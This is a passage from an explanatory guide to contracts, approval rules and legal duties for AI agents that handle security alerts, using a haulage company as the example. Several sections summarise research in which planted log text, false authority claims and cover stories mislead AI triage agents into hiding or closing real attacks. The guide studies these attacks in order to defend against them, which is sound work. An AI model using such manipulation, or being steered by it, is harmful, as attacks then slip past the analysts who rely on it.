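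Tsegai and colleagues also built an agent that may close an alert only if it has positive evidence of harmless activity or has investigated thoroughly enough. It missed 3.1% of the attack alerts, while the best of the other five missed 40.4%. It sent 18.4% of all alerts to analysts, close to the 18% that were attacks. The new design also added a second AI to challenge each verdict and a third to decide, so these results can't be attributed to the stricter closing rule alone.

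### Attaching the limits to each request

A table of destinations has little effect if one component follows it and the next ignores it. Fatouros and colleagues, whose approval tiers for financial companies came up earlier, propose a runtime, the software that runs the agents and connects them to tools, in which every request carries its own limits. They call these limits the Security Context. It contains:

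- the organisation, the user and the user's role;
- the data scope and the classification level;
- the permitted tools, document collections and parts of a knowledge graph;
- where the request came from, such as an analyst's question, an alert or a schedule;
- a token for the audit log, and the times at which the context was created and expires.

When an employee reports an email, the runtime creates a Security Context for the case. If the agent requests the company's phishing playbook, the runtime checks that the playbook's collection is on the list of permitted collections and that the classification level allows access. If the agent requests personnel files, the runtime refuses and logs which rule the request broke. Eight such checks cover tool calls, memory, reports and what appears on an analyst's screen, among other things. A request with no Security Context fails automatically.

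The context cannot change during a case. A component may pass on a narrower version but never a broader one, so an agent can't gain access by handing its work to another agent. The organisation can also give the agents a profile with its contacts, terminology and classification rules. The profile goes into the model's prompt but grants no permissions, so writing "this agent may read all mailboxes" in it has no effect on the checks.

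Where feasible, findings refer to sensitive evidence instead of copying it. In the paper's example of a suspicious email, the finding points to the message in the mail store. But the audit log records every prompt, and it accepts new entries but no edits. If it stores prompts in full, the email text ends up there anyway. An organisation that adopted the design would need to decide how long to keep log entries before switching the log on.

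The design keeps organisations apart by checking an organisation identifier whenever an agent reads or writes memory, and by limiting which document collections each request can reach. That suits a bank with its own installation. An MDR provider that serves many customers from one installation also needs to keep those customers apart, but its analysts may all work under the provider's identifier. Fatouros and colleagues say this use requires an additional field, `tenant_id`, to identify the customer. Their published Security Context doesn't include the field, and the checks would also have to use it.

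The Security Context also has no field for destinations. It can forbid a tool altogether, but the haulage company's rule that a reputation service may receive only a domain would have to go in the rules for that tool's inputs or in the network controls.

All of this exists only as a design. The paper describes a small version that someone could build and a test, not yet run, that would attempt forbidden access at each of the eight checks. To pass, the runtime would have to refuse and log every attempt. Passing would not show that the design protects against planted text in data the agent is allowed to read. The paper leaves that problem to other safeguards, such as human review and detection of suspicious inputs.

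### When the evidence is misleading

Pandey and Bhujang (2026), in *Poisoning the Watchtower*, measured how often such text succeeds. They created artificial security logs, added misleading text to the malicious entries, and asked GPT-4o-mini to label the entries, summarise them or recommend a response. They tested four kinds of text against four levels of defence on each of these three tasks, with 120 malicious entries in each of the 48 combinations. The table shows how often the text worked, averaged over the four kinds.

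| Defence | Labels | Summaries | Recommendations | Average |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 21% | 38% | 21% | 27% |
| Log fields marked as untrusted data | 8% | 31% | 13% | 17% |
| Marking and a filter for suspicious phrases | 11% | 19% | 9% | 13% |
| Marking and a fixed set of answers | 12% | 16% | 8% | 12% |

Results varied widely by type of attack. Plain orders to ignore earlier instructions never changed a label. False claims of authority got 68% of malicious entries labelled harmless when there was no defence, and 15% when the fields were marked as untrusted. That figure rose to 33% with a fixed set of answers, even though this was the best defence on average.

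Text that imitated the system's own formatting corrupted 96% of the undefended summaries. Nearly all of the corrupted summaries left out the attack or played it down rather than calling it harmless outright, so software that checked only for the word "benign" would have missed them. The experiment used artificial logs and one older model without tools, so the percentages may not apply to current products.

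Agents that can act on what they read present a greater danger. *When AIOps Become "AI Oops"* (Pasquini, Kornaropoulos and colleagues, 2026) examines agents that diagnose and repair faults in IT systems. It shows that an outsider with no access to the system could plant a false explanation of a fault, along with a harmful repair, in the records the agents read. Agents using GPT-4o and GPT-4.1 adopted such repairs, and the planted text got past commercial filters for prompt injection. In one case, the agent added the correct version number of the affected software to the false explanation. Details like that could persuade a reviewer to approve the repair, so the reviewer needs to see the original records as well as the agent's account.

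Their defence removes or neutralises text from outside users before the agent sees it. In their tests, it blocked the attacks without making the agents worse at their normal work. This works because an agent repairing a server rarely needs to know what a visitor typed. An agent that detects phishing can't use the defence in the same way, since outside text is the evidence it has to judge.

Canale tested a different safeguard on newer models. Planted instructions almost never worked, but cover stories did, such as a claim that the operations team had authorised the activity. A program wrote the cover stories and revised them after seeing each verdict, an advantage few real attackers would have. The small Gemini model wrongly closed 19 of 46 attacks without manipulation, and the program got it to close 56% of the rest within eight attempts. Gemini 4 wrongly closed 4 of 28 without manipulation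 and 17% of the rest with it.

The safeguard was a fixed policy outside the model. Alerts with a high risk score went straight to analysts, and the model could close the others only if it reported high confidence. This policy alone reduced the program's success against the small model from 56% to 30%. In a complete system, which also combined related signals before passing them to the model, 102 of the 127 detected attacks reached analysts whatever the model decided. The program targeted seven of the remaining attacks and hid none of them completely, because each had also set off another alert.

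When Canale ran the complete system on three new simulated periods, Gemini 4 missed four attacks without being manipulated. This is a reason to have a person check a sample of the reports the phishing agent closes, even if the agent reads only what the table allows.

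## Writing approval and escalation rules

The isolation rule requires the incident response lead to approve the isolation of any server, but an approval rule must also specify what she sees when the request arrives, how long the agent waits for her, and what it does if she is asleep. An escalation rule must specify the same things. It passes a case to a person even when the agent has no action to propose, as when the phishing agent finds that an employee has replied to an attacker.

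A complete rule has six parts. For its servers, the haulage company might fill them in like this:

| Part | Rule for isolating a server |
|---|---|
| Trigger | The agent proposes to isolate any server |
| Evidence shown to the approver | What the server does, what work would stop, the original log entries and the agent's reasons |
| Approver and deputy | The on-call incident response lead, then the SOC manager |
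| Time limit | Ten minutes for each of them |
| Default if nobody answers | The agent isolates the server and keeps calling both |
| Who can reverse it | The lead, the SOC manager or the systems engineer on night duty |

If the agent acts because the lead and the SOC manager are both asleep, neither of them can undo a mistake, so somebody who is awake needs the authority to reconnect the server. Each approval should cover one exact action. If the agent changes its request from one server to two after the lead has read it, it needs new approval.

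### The Sophos agreement

A company that hires an MDR provider starts from the provider's terms. *Managed Detection and Response and Managed Detection and Response Plus*, a service description Sophos last revised in October 2026, is part of the security company's legal agreement with each customer. During onboarding, the customer chooses how much Sophos may do without asking.

| Mode | What Sophos may do |
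|---|---|
| Authorize | Act against a threat and notify the customer afterwards |
| Collaborate | Investigate, but act only with the customer's written consent, apart from steps such as remote queries and evidence collection |
| Collaborate then Authorize | Ask first, but switch to Authorize if no contact acknowledges the request |
| Notify Only | Investigate and give guidance, leaving the customer to act |

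Collaborate then Authorize comes closest to the six-part rule. The customer must name at least one primary and one alternate contact, each with the authority to approve response actions, so there is an approver and a deputy. If nobody answers, the default is that Sophos may act once it has made "reasonable attempts" to reach every contact, but the description sets no limit in minutes. An older help page, Sophos' *MDR threat response*, specifies attempts by phone. Customers also agree to make commercially reasonable efforts to acknowledge Sophos within 60 minutes in serious cases, but no term ties Sophos' permission to act to that deadline.

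The default also depends on acknowledgement rather than a decision. If the SOC manager answers the phone and says he must ask the operations director first, he has acknowledged the request. On a literal reading, Sophos must then keep waiting for written consent while the attack continues. The company can prevent this itself by telling its contacts to approve, refuse or hand the call to the deputy.

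How Sophos contacts the customer depends on how serious it judges the case to be.

| Severity | Examples | Contact |
|---|---|---|
| Critical | Active ransomware, data theft, an attacker moving between machines | Sophos phones, either to confirm what it has done or to ask for approval |
| High | Confirmed malware contacting its operator, a compromised account | A case update if Sophos has contained the threat, and a phone call if it has not or if it needs the customer |
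| Medium | Isolated suspicious activity, common malware that the software blocked | A case update or email, with no phone call |

Under Authorize, Sophos could isolate the server that assigns drivers to lorries and, if it judged a High case contained, report it in writing without phoning anyone. The company might then learn of the isolation from its drivers. A customer that chooses Authorize therefore needs someone to watch the case updates overnight, or its own alarm for important servers going offline.

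Sophos's description sets a target of two minutes to open a case after a detection arrives, and another 30 minutes to take an initial action. Sophos states that these targets are not a service level agreement, the part of a contract that commits a supplier to a measured standard. The initial action can be contacting the customer, collecting evidence or starting a response, so Sophos can meet the target while the attacker still has access.

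Under the more expensive tier, MDR Plus, Sophos commits to contacting the customer within 60 minutes in 90% of serious cases each month, or to starting a response in that time if the customer has chosen Authorize. Sophos fails to meet the agreement only if it misses this target in more than three months out of twelve. The customer can then claim a credit towards its next subscription of 5% of the previous billing cycle's fees or $5,000, whichever is less.

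Under Sophos's liability terms, the customer acknowledges that changes it authorises could interrupt its systems, and that refusing them could let an attack start or get worse. If the customer denies a request, Sophos is not liable for damage from the resulting attack. A SOC manager who refuses an isolation to keep the lorries moving therefore takes that risk on the company's behalf, and the company should record whether he has the authority to do so.

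The clause covers refusals but doesn't mention unanswered requests. Another term, though, relieves Sophos of responsibility for communication failures when the customer's contacts are unavailable. ThreatDown (2026), the service description for a Malwarebytes MDR service, is more explicit and excludes liability for any harm caused by a customer's late reply.

### Whether an analyst or software acts

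Sophos's modes apply to both human analysts and software. The description defines a response action as one that Sophos performs "manually or through Sophos's automated systems". A customer that chooses Authorize therefore authorises the software as well as the analysts. Under Collaborate, both need written consent. Sophos's separate list of supported actions, which includes isolating computers, disabling accounts and blocking addresses, doesn't distinguish between analysts and software either.

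Approval rules matter because software handles many security cases and lacks an analyst's hesitation about disconnecting a server that looks important. Aaron Bugal, a field chief information security officer at Sophos, told PCQuest that autonomous functions review, resolve and close more than half of the company's managed detection and response (MDR) cases. Many of those cases probably needed no containment, so the figure doesn't show how often software isolates a machine. But Bugal also described protective steps that can begin before an investigation is complete, such as stopping a user from opening more sessions.

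The terms of another MDR provider, eSentire, have the same gap. According to eSentire's *Atlas MDR Enhanced Package* (2026), an alert may lead to an automated notification, "automated AI-led investigation and response", review by a human analyst, or some combination of these. The document mentions the AI more explicitly than Sophos's does, but it gives the customer no setting to choose among these responses.

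Some providers let customers vary the rules by machine, user or action. eSentire's *Endpoint Services* (2024), an older set of terms, authorises isolation of every machine unless the client lists it as a critical asset that needs written authorisation. That would suit the haulage company better than a single mode, because the company wants fast action on laptops and a phone call about servers. Customers of Microsoft's Defender Experts service can exclude sensitive devices and users, for which Microsoft's staff then only give guidance, but customers can't set different rules for different actions. In another of its MDR services, Sophos lets customers approve some containment actions in advance through playbooks they create.

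Where the MDR terms do require a person, that person's decision often starts a clock. The 60 minutes in Sophos's MDR Plus commitment begin when Sophos personnel classify the case as serious. At ThreatDown, an alert counts as a "Critical Incident" only after an analyst has confirmed it. These conditions determine when the customer can claim a credit, and any delay before the analyst looks at the case doesn't count.

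Some products already let security teams decide where the AI acts alone and where it stops for a person's approval. Help Net Security's *SentinelOne expands security operations automation with governed AI* describes one such release. This is the supplier's own account, but it suggests that the setting is feasible. A customer of an MDR service could ask the provider which actions its software can start without an analyst, and have the answer written into the agreement.

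### Acting first or waiting for approval

A rough calculation can help decide which actions should wait. Let p be the chance that the alert is real, H the harm that an attack does per minute, t the wait for approval in minutes, and W the cost of a wrong action. Acting first is better on average when:

p × H × t > (1 − p) × W

The left side is the expected harm while the agent waits, and the right side is the expected loss from acting by mistake. The inequality extends the earlier confidence threshold to account for time, because the harm that early isolation prevents is now H × t.

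Suppose an alert has a 90% chance of being real, an attack does $500 of damage a minute, and approval takes 20 minutes. Wrongly isolating a workstation costs $2,000, and wrongly isolating a server costs $150,000. These figures are invented.

| | Workstation | Server |
|---|---|---|
| Expected harm from waiting | $9,000 | $9,000 |
| Expected cost of a wrong action | $200 | $15,000 |
| Better choice | Act | Wait |
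| Wait at which the two costs are equal | 27 seconds | 33 minutes |

For the workstation, hardly any approver could answer fast enough to make asking worthwhile. For the server, asking is worthwhile if the answer comes within about 33 minutes. A small change in p can also change the choice for the server. At 90% the agent should wait, but at 95% it should act, because the harm from waiting is $9,500 and the expected cost of a mistake is $7,500. Few tools can estimate p precisely enough to justify treating 90% and 95% differently. The choice for the workstation stays the same for any p above about 17%.

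The last row of the table also helps with the default. The haulage company's rule gives the lead and the SOC manager ten minutes each. If neither has answered after 20 minutes, the choice depends on how much longer an answer will take, not on the harm already done. Both are probably asleep, so it could take hours. With these figures, the agent should then isolate the server, even though it was right to ask first.

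The formula assumes that harm builds up steadily, but a thief who has finished copying a database does little more damage by staying another ten minutes, while ransomware may do most of its damage in the first few. It also assumes that isolation stops the attack, which is wrong if the attacker has already reached another machine. Finally, it treats W as fixed, but a wrongly isolated server costs more every hour until somebody reconnects it.

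An attacker could also exploit the default by setting off an alert at three in the morning, when nobody will answer, to get the server taken offline. A less drastic default, such as blocking the server's internet connections but leaving the depots connected, would reduce that risk and let drivers get their assignments while the agent keeps calling. Another problem is that some harms, such as a hospital losing access to patient records, don't have a sensible price per minute.

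### How many requests an approver can handle

The calculation uses a fixed wait, but the actual wait grows with the approver's workload. If an agent sends 120 requests a day and each takes four minutes to judge, the approver needs eight hours, her whole shift. If rules settle the routine cases and only 18 exceptions reach her, she needs 72 minutes.

Even 18 requests can be too many if they arrive together, as they may during an attack. If ten arrive at once, the approver needs 40 minutes to finish them all, but a server isolation should wait no more than 33 minutes. The queue should therefore rank requests by the harm a delay would cause, and the deputy should take some of them when the queue gets long.

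*The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) finds that approval of every action is "already showing strain". It cites Microsoft's argument, in a response to a US government consultation, that only higher-impact or uncertain actions should go to human reviewers. It also cites Google DeepMind work that anticipates attacks designed to wear approvers down or show them harmless-looking summaries. *AI Agents Push Humans Out of the Loop* (2026) also recommends saving people's attention for decisions that need human judgement. It adds that supervising an automated system erodes the skills needed to supervise it, so an approver who only ever approves may become worse at judging the rare case that matters.

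Sending people fewer approval requests doesn't by itself make them more careful with the ones that remain. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 people from outside the software industry supervise an AI assistant through a simulated day. The assistant proposed 18 actions, seven of which went beyond its task, such as reading private messages or buying a lounge pass. One group approved or refused every action. Another first set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of action, then decided only the cases their rules sent back to them.

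| | Approved every action | Set rules first |
|---|---|---|
| Average number of requests | 18 | 10.9 |
| Share of out-of-task requests approved | 40.3% | 66.8% |
| Out-of-task actions blocked overall | 59.6% | 39.6% |

The people who set rules chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so they mostly put off the decisions. The approval rates aren't strictly comparable, because this group never saw the requests that "allow" and "never" rules had already settled, and Yan assigned some of its members after the random assignment had ended. Some of the out-of-task actions were also ones a user might welcome, such as phoning the airport to confirm a flight, which nearly everyone allowed. Still, the "never" rules blocked 31 actions without anyone having to refuse them. A SOC that wants to cut 120 requests to 18 should similarly decide the other 102 in advance, by allowing or forbidding each kind of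 action.

### Why people approve too readily

Automation bias is the tendency to accept a machine's output and discount evidence against it. The *International AI Safety Report 2026* (2026) describes a randomised experiment in which 2,784 participants checked labels suggested by an AI. They corrected its mistakes less often when a correction took extra effort or when they viewed AI more favourably. An approval screen can create the same problem if approving takes one click but refusing requires a written explanation.

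The evidence for automation bias is weaker among professionals doing their own jobs. *Survey for Categorising Explainable AI Studies Using Data Analysis Task Frameworks* (2025) counts nine studies that found automation bias and four that did not. Five of the nine used paid online workers on tasks in which they had no stake, such as predicting whether a criminal would reoffend. The four that found no bias all used experts on tasks that fitted their work, and the studies that did find bias under similar conditions found much less of it.

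Bono (2025), in *Randomized Controlled Trials for Phishing Triage Agent*, found a similar result in security when testing Microsoft's agent for sorting reported emails. Analysts who used the agent were 77% more accurate than those who did not. They gave malicious emails 53% more of their time and showed little tendency to rubber-stamp the agent's malicious verdicts. However, Microsoft both sells the agent and ran the trial. The finding about rubber-stamping also concerns malicious verdicts, whereas an analyst who accepts a wrong "harmless" verdict lets the attack through. Approving a server isolation also differs from judging an email, because wrongly approving or wrongly refusing it can do serious harm. *Decision-Aware Trust Signal Alignment for SOC Alert Triage* (2026) notes that researchers have rarely studied how an alert's presentation affects escalation decisions, especially when the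 two kinds of error have different consequences.

### Helping approvers judge a request

A SOC can change the evidence it shows approvers. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, studied actions that look harmless until the approver knows what came before. In their example, a user tells an agent to send an auditor only the totals from some invoices. Hidden instructions in a supplier's note cause the agent to copy the full invoices into a file, which it then asks to send to the auditor. The tool and the recipient are both permitted, so the approver can spot the problem only if she knows where the file's contents came from.

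The researchers showed 80 volunteers 12 requests each, half of them unsafe, on one of four screens.

| What the screen showed | Unsafe requests approved | Safe requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The exact details of the action | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| The details, the user's instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
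| The same facts arranged around the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more information. Arranging it around the consequence may have helped further. After adjustment, that arrangement did 7.9 percentage points better than the full log, but the 95% interval ran from 19.7 points better to 3.8 points worse, and the researchers did not preregister their analysis. When a violation depended on how several steps were linked, people approved 7 of 30 unsafe requests with each screen.

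The best-performing approval screen quoted the user's original restriction, showed the exact action, stated its combined effect in one sentence and linked that sentence to the records behind it. For a server isolation, the sentence might read "Isolating this server will stop driver assignments at all depots, and the alert rests on one login record." Software outside the agent should write this sentence, because an agent that an attacker has misled would probably write a misleading summary. That software can also miss violations. In a separate test, the monitor that Hossain and colleagues built for this purpose detected 89.2% of them, and the approver would have seen no warning about the rest.

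The act-or-wait formula assumes that the approver stops every mistake. If she lets through a share a of the wrong isolations, waiting saves only (1 − a) × (1 − p) × W. In the server example, the saving falls to $9,000 when a is 40%, which equals the expected harm from waiting. Waiting would be a net loss if her error rate were 55%, like that of the volunteers given the short description, but would still be worthwhile at 24.2%. The volunteers were not security analysts, so their error rates are only a rough guide. Waiting is also less worthwhile if the approver refuses some justified isolations.

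Another remedy is to have the approver decide before she sees the AI's recommendation. *Cybernetic and Epistemic* (2026) reports that Buçinca, Malaya and Gajos tested this in 2021 and found that it reduced over-reliance, but that people preferred and trusted designs that didn't require it. It also takes time, because the approver must work through the evidence herself. The haulage company could reserve it for servers, where the lead would read the log entries and record her own view before seeing the agent's recommendation.

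*Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) also recommends that reviewers give a reason whether they agree or disagree with the AI, and that organisations check a sample of the agreements for rubber-stamping. Asking for a reason either way removes the incentive to approve just to avoid typing. Checking a sample is practical once the number of requests is low. With 18 requests a day, rechecking one in ten at four minutes each would take a second analyst about 50 minutes a week.

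## Putting the limits into the supplier's agreement

The supplier has to follow an approval rule only if the legal agreement includes it. Vague wording such as "reasonable containment measures" would leave the haulage company with a weak claim for its lost deliveries. A buyer can avoid this by writing its rules into the agreement, along with terms that let it check whether the supplier follows them.

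### The clauses a buyer needs

The most important one is an annex of permitted actions. It lists each response action, the machines and accounts it may affect and the approval it needs, and it forbids everything else. The haulage company's annex would contain the isolation rule, so nobody would argue later about what "reasonable" meant. Such arguments are likely, since about a quarter of organisations in the Illumio survey described earlier had an AI start an action nobody had approved, according to Help Net Security. The annex should be a separate document that the SOC manager and the supplier can amend in writing, because the isolation rule may change every quarter. It should specify which takes priority if the annex and the product's settings differ.

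A second clause covers changes to the model. A supplier can replace the model behind a tool without changing anything the analysts see, and the new model may choose different actions from the same evidence. Three months of accurate isolations by the old model are therefore poor evidence about the new one. The clause might require 30 days' notice before the supplier changes the model, its instructions or its tools, and let the customer require approval for every action until the customer has tested the change. Suppliers will reasonably object to waiting 30 days to send out protection against a new attack, so the parties can exempt those updates if the supplier tries them on a few machines first.

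The data-processing instructions oblige the supplier to follow the table of destinations from the phishing example. They prohibit the supplier from keeping email text for longer than agreed or using it to train models. The supplier may rent its model from one company and its servers from another, so a clause on subcontractors applies the same limits to them. The clause also requires the supplier to list its subcontractors, notify the customer of any change and allow the customer to object. Without this clause, employees' emails could reach a company that the customer has never assessed.

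Two more clauses give the customer evidence. The first requires the supplier to send the trace, the ordered record of what the agent did or tried to do, to storage the customer controls. Each entry should include the model version and any approval. If only the supplier holds the trace, the customer has to rely on the supplier for evidence in a dispute about the supplier's conduct. The second gives the customer audit rights, which cover what a trace can't show, such as which supplier employees can change the agent's permissions.

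The incident-notice clause should require the supplier to report any action outside the annex within a fixed time, even if the action did no harm. A clause written for data breaches wouldn't cover an agent that isolates the wrong server, because no data leaked and no attacker got in.

The liability clause sets out who pays when the tool isolates a system by mistake. A supplier's warranty may not cover the loss. CrowdStrike, for example, offers customers of its Falcon Complete service a limited warranty for certain costs of a cybersecurity breach, but a depot left idle by a mistaken isolation hasn't suffered a breach.

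The exit clause lets the customer leave after repeated violations and take its data and traces with it. It also requires both sides to close the agent's accounts on the last day. Otherwise, a former supplier's software might still be able to disconnect the customer's computers.

### Noticing and proving a breach

A customer can check some of these clauses from its own records, but for others it depends on the supplier.

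| Clause | How the customer might notice a breach | What would prove it |
|---|---|---|
| Permitted actions | An isolation has no matching approval | The trace and the annex in force that day |
| Model changes | The version in the trace changes, or test alerts get different answers | Version records and the date of the supplier's notice |
| Data instructions | A decoy address planted in one mailbox receives a message | Network logs and the supplier's processing records |
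| Subcontractors | The tool's traffic goes to an unlisted company | Network logs or the supplier's hosting records |
| Access to logs | A laptop's own log shows an action missing from the trace | The two logs side by side |
| Audit rights | The supplier refuses or keeps postponing | The written request and the reply |
| Incident notice | The customer finds the incident first | The supplier's internal ticket, with its time |
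| Liability | The supplier rejects a valid claim | The trace and the company's record of its losses |
| Exit | An old account tries to log in | Login records |

An unannounced model change is among the hardest violations to prove, because a language model can give different answers to the same alert even when nobody has changed it. The customer therefore has to run its test many times. Suppose the agent proposed isolation in 9 of 10 runs last month and 7 of 10 this month. The difference is 20 percentage points, but its standard error is about 17 points, so chance could easily explain it. If the agent had instead proposed isolation in 90 of 100 runs and then 70 of 100, the standard error would be about 5.5 points, and chance would be an unlikely explanation. Even then, the supplier may have changed the agent's instructions rather than the model, so the notice clause should cover both.

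Training on the customer's data may leave no sign that the customer can see. A decoy address would reveal that someone used or leaked it, but a model could learn from thousands of emails without repeating one. Only an audit of the supplier's training records is likely to show whether the data was used for training, and the audit would have to cover any subcontractor that trains the model.

### What EU law already requires

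Two European laws make some of these clauses compulsory. Article 28 of the General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), formally the European Union's *Regulation (EU) 2016/679 of the European Parliament and of the Council* (2016), applies when one organisation handles personal data for another. The organisation that decides why and how to use the data is the controller, and the one that handles it for the controller is the processor. A company that hires an MDR provider is normally the controller of its employees' emails, and the provider is its processor.

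The other law, the Digital Operational Resilience Act (DORA), covers banks, insurers and other financial firms. The rules for these firms' agreements with technology suppliers are in the European Union's *Article 30 Key contractual provisions* (2022). Some of the rules apply to every agreement, while others, marked with an asterisk in the table, apply only if the service supports a "critical or important function" of the firm.

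| Clause | GDPR Article 28 | DORA Article 30 |
|---|---|---|
| Permitted actions | Documented instructions, but only for processing personal data | A "clear and complete description" of the services |
| Model changes | Nothing specific | Notice of developments that could materially affect the agreed service levels* |
| Data instructions | The purpose, duration and types of data, and processing only as instructed | Data protection terms, data locations and notice before a location changes |
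| Subcontractors | Written authorisation, with the same data protection duties passed on | Whether the supplier may subcontract important functions, and on what conditions |
| Access to logs | Information needed to show compliance | Access to relevant records, and copies of those critical to the supplier's work* |
| Audit rights | Audits and inspections | Unrestricted access, inspection and audit* |
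| Incident notice | Help with the controller's duties after a data breach | Help during an incident, free or at a price agreed beforehand |
| Liability | The processor answers for its subcontractors' data protection failures | No rule on who pays or how much |
| Exit | Deletion or return of the data, as the controller chooses | Termination rights and return of data, plus a transition period* |

Under Article 28 of the GDPR, the controller can authorise each subcontractor separately or give a general authorisation. With a general authorisation, the processor must tell the controller about planned changes and let it object, but the article sets no minimum notice period, so the agreement should set one. Article 33 requires the processor to report a personal data breach to the controller "without undue delay" but leaves the parties to agree on the number of hours.

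Article 28 helps against an agent that reads too much. If the phishing agent opens the finance director's mailbox against written instructions, the supplier has probably broken the terms that the article requires. The article helps much less if the agent isolates the server that assigns drivers to lorries, because the company's complaint is about lost deliveries and hardly concerns personal data.

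Under another paragraph of the article, a processor that decides for itself why and how to process personal data counts as a controller for that processing. An agent that chooses its own searches while investigating a reported email is probably still working within the customer's purpose. A supplier that uses the same emails to improve a product for other customers is much more likely to have become a controller.

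DORA comes closer to covering an agent's actions because it concerns the whole service. But a description such as "detection and containment on all company devices" might satisfy Article 30 without specifying which devices the agent may isolate on its own. A standard addendum may not add that detail. The *DORA Addendum* from BIT, a Dutch internet company, takes its definition of "Services" from the regulation and applies it to whatever the main agreement provides. With an addendum like that, the list of permitted actions has to go in the main agreement.

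The rule on notice of material developments has a similar weakness. Suppose a new model responds to alerts faster but isolates twice as many healthy machines. If the agreed service levels measure only speed, the supplier still meets them and can argue that it has nothing to report. A bank should therefore add a limit on mistaken isolations to the service levels.

The model's developer may also count as a subcontractor under DORA. A separate EU regulation, made under Article 30(5) of DORA, sets out what a financial firm must assess before it lets a supplier subcontract services that support critical or important functions.

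Neither article mentions actions that software chooses for itself, requires a person to approve them, or assigns the cost of wrong ones. The haulage company isn't a financial firm, so DORA doesn't apply to it, but it can still copy the clauses on audit and exit. Some financial regulators also hold named individuals at the customer responsible. Nandakumara told Help Net Security that Britain's senior managers regime and Australia's financial regulator, APRA, both expect a named individual to be responsible for the results of AI. A bank can recover money from its supplier under the agreement, but that individual remains responsible.

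### Whether the AI Act adds duties

An AI tool that only investigates alerts and contains attacks is probably not "high-risk" under the EU's AI Act, even if it can shut down servers. The high-risk category carries the heaviest duties for systems that are allowed on the market, and it includes AI used as a safety component in running critical digital infrastructure. But recital 55, part of the Act's explanatory preamble, excludes components intended solely for cybersecurity from that description. Some uncertainty remains because courts use recitals to interpret a law, but recitals don't have the force of its articles.

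A security tool could still qualify as high-risk because the list also includes systems that monitor and evaluate workers' behaviour or performance. Software that scores employees on how likely they are to steal data might fall under this heading, whereas there is a better case for excluding a tool that only detects unusual logins. An organisation that uses a high-risk tool must assign competent people to oversee it and must keep any logs under the organisation's control for at least six months. An employer must also tell the affected workers about the tool.

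A smaller duty can apply to ordinary security agents. If an agent messages an employee to ask whether she logged in from Lyon, its provider must have designed it so that she knows it is an AI, unless that is obvious. None of these duties specifies which servers a supplier's agent may isolate.

### Delta v. CrowdStrike

An American lawsuit is testing what a security supplier may change on a customer's machines. CrowdStrike's Falcon software detects attacks on individual computers. On 19 July 2024, a faulty update from the company crashed more than 8.5 million Windows computers, according to the complaint Delta Air Lines (2024) filed that October in a state court in Fulton County, Georgia. Delta cancelled about 7,000 flights over five days and claims more than $500 million in out-of-pocket losses.

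Part of Falcon runs in the kernel, the core of the operating system, where a fault can crash the whole computer. Delta had opted out of automatic updates, as CrowdStrike allowed its customers to do. Delta alleges that CrowdStrike nevertheless used "content updates" to change how Falcon behaved in the kernel, without Delta's consent or Microsoft's certification. Delta calls this an "unauthorized door" into its systems. The complaint also alleges that a test on a single computer would have exposed the fault.

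Delta sued for breach of contract, computer trespass, gross negligence, fraud and several other wrongs. The claims beyond breach of contract matter because the agreement limits what Delta can recover. CRN's *CrowdStrike Seeks Dismissal For Most Of Delta Lawsuit Claims* reports that CrowdStrike, in a lawsuit of its own, said the limit was twice the fees. If Delta can prove a wrong that the limit doesn't cover, it could recover far more.

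CrowdStrike acknowledges the update was flawed but says the subscription agreement authorised it to access and update Delta's systems, according to ch-aviation's *US court allows Delta to pursue lawsuit over cyber outage*. It also relies on Georgia's economic loss rule, which generally stops a party from suing over a broken contract as if it were some other civil wrong. NBC Philadelphia reports that CrowdStrike argued Delta was trying to get around the agreement. CrowdStrike and Microsoft have separately blamed Delta's slow recovery on outdated systems and Delta's refusal of their help.

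Reuters' *Delta can sue CrowdStrike over computer outage that caused 7,000 canceled flights* (2025) reported that on 16 May 2025 Judge Kelly Lee Ellerbe allowed much of the case to continue. According to CRN's *5 Things To Watch In Delta’s Lawsuit Against CrowdStrike*, she held on the trespass claim that Delta had "sufficiently alleged" that CrowdStrike knowingly accessed its computers without authorisation, given Delta's choice about automatic updates. She also allowed the gross negligence claim, noting that CrowdStrike's president had said publicly that the company did something "horribly wrong".

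The judge rejected Delta's fraud claim for any statements made before 30 June 2022, the date of the agreement. A narrower claim about the alleged back door survived, according to ITPro's *CrowdStrike prepares for battle as Delta given go-ahead for outage lawsuit*. She also wasn't persuaded by Delta's general arguments against the economic loss rule, though the rule didn't end the trespass or gross negligence claims at that stage. Delta had already withdrawn its claims for product liability and deceptive business practices.

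At this stage, a judge assumes the allegations are true and asks only whether they would support a claim, so the ruling didn't establish that CrowdStrike trespassed. CrowdStrike's report for the quarter to 30 April 2026 describes the case as still in discovery, when the two sides exchange evidence. Computer Weekly's *Texas judge throws out second lawsuit over CrowdStrike outage* reports that a federal judge dismissed two other lawsuits over the outage, one by airline passengers in June 2025 and one by shareholders in January 2026.

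CrowdStrike's lawyer expects the agreement to limit any surviving claims to "the single-digit-millions of dollars", which is less than 2% of Delta's claimed losses. In the earlier invented example, a wrongly isolated server cost the haulage company $150,000. If the company paid $60,000 in fees and the agreement capped claims at twice the fees, it could recover at most $120,000, leaving a loss of $30,000 even if it won completely. A buyer can ask for a higher cap on liability for harm from actions outside the annex, though the supplier may charge more for it.

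The comparison with AI holds for the question of authority. CrowdStrike relies on a general permission in the agreement, and Delta on a specific setting that it says CrowdStrike overrode. An MDR customer could have the same dispute if its agreement allows containment in general but its settings require approval for servers. The case also shows why an annex should define "update" and state whether the term includes detection files, models and the instructions given to them. A customer that switches off automatic updates may think it has refused every change, while the supplier thinks the setting covers only new versions of the program.

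The comparison is weaker on fault. CrowdStrike sent one faulty file to many customers, whereas an AI agent chooses an action for one customer based on evidence it has just read. The trespass claim depends on CrowdStrike having known that it lacked authorisation. If an agent isolates a server against the rules, the supplier could argue that none of its staff knew. Testing on one computer might have revealed the faulty file, but no single test can show how an agent will respond to every future alert. A supplier that never tested its agent would still be in a weak position, but fault would be harder to judge if the supplier had tested it badly.

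### Limits set by the model's maker

Many security suppliers build their tools on a model from another company, such as OpenAI or Anthropic. They must follow that company's usage policies, which the customer may never have seen.

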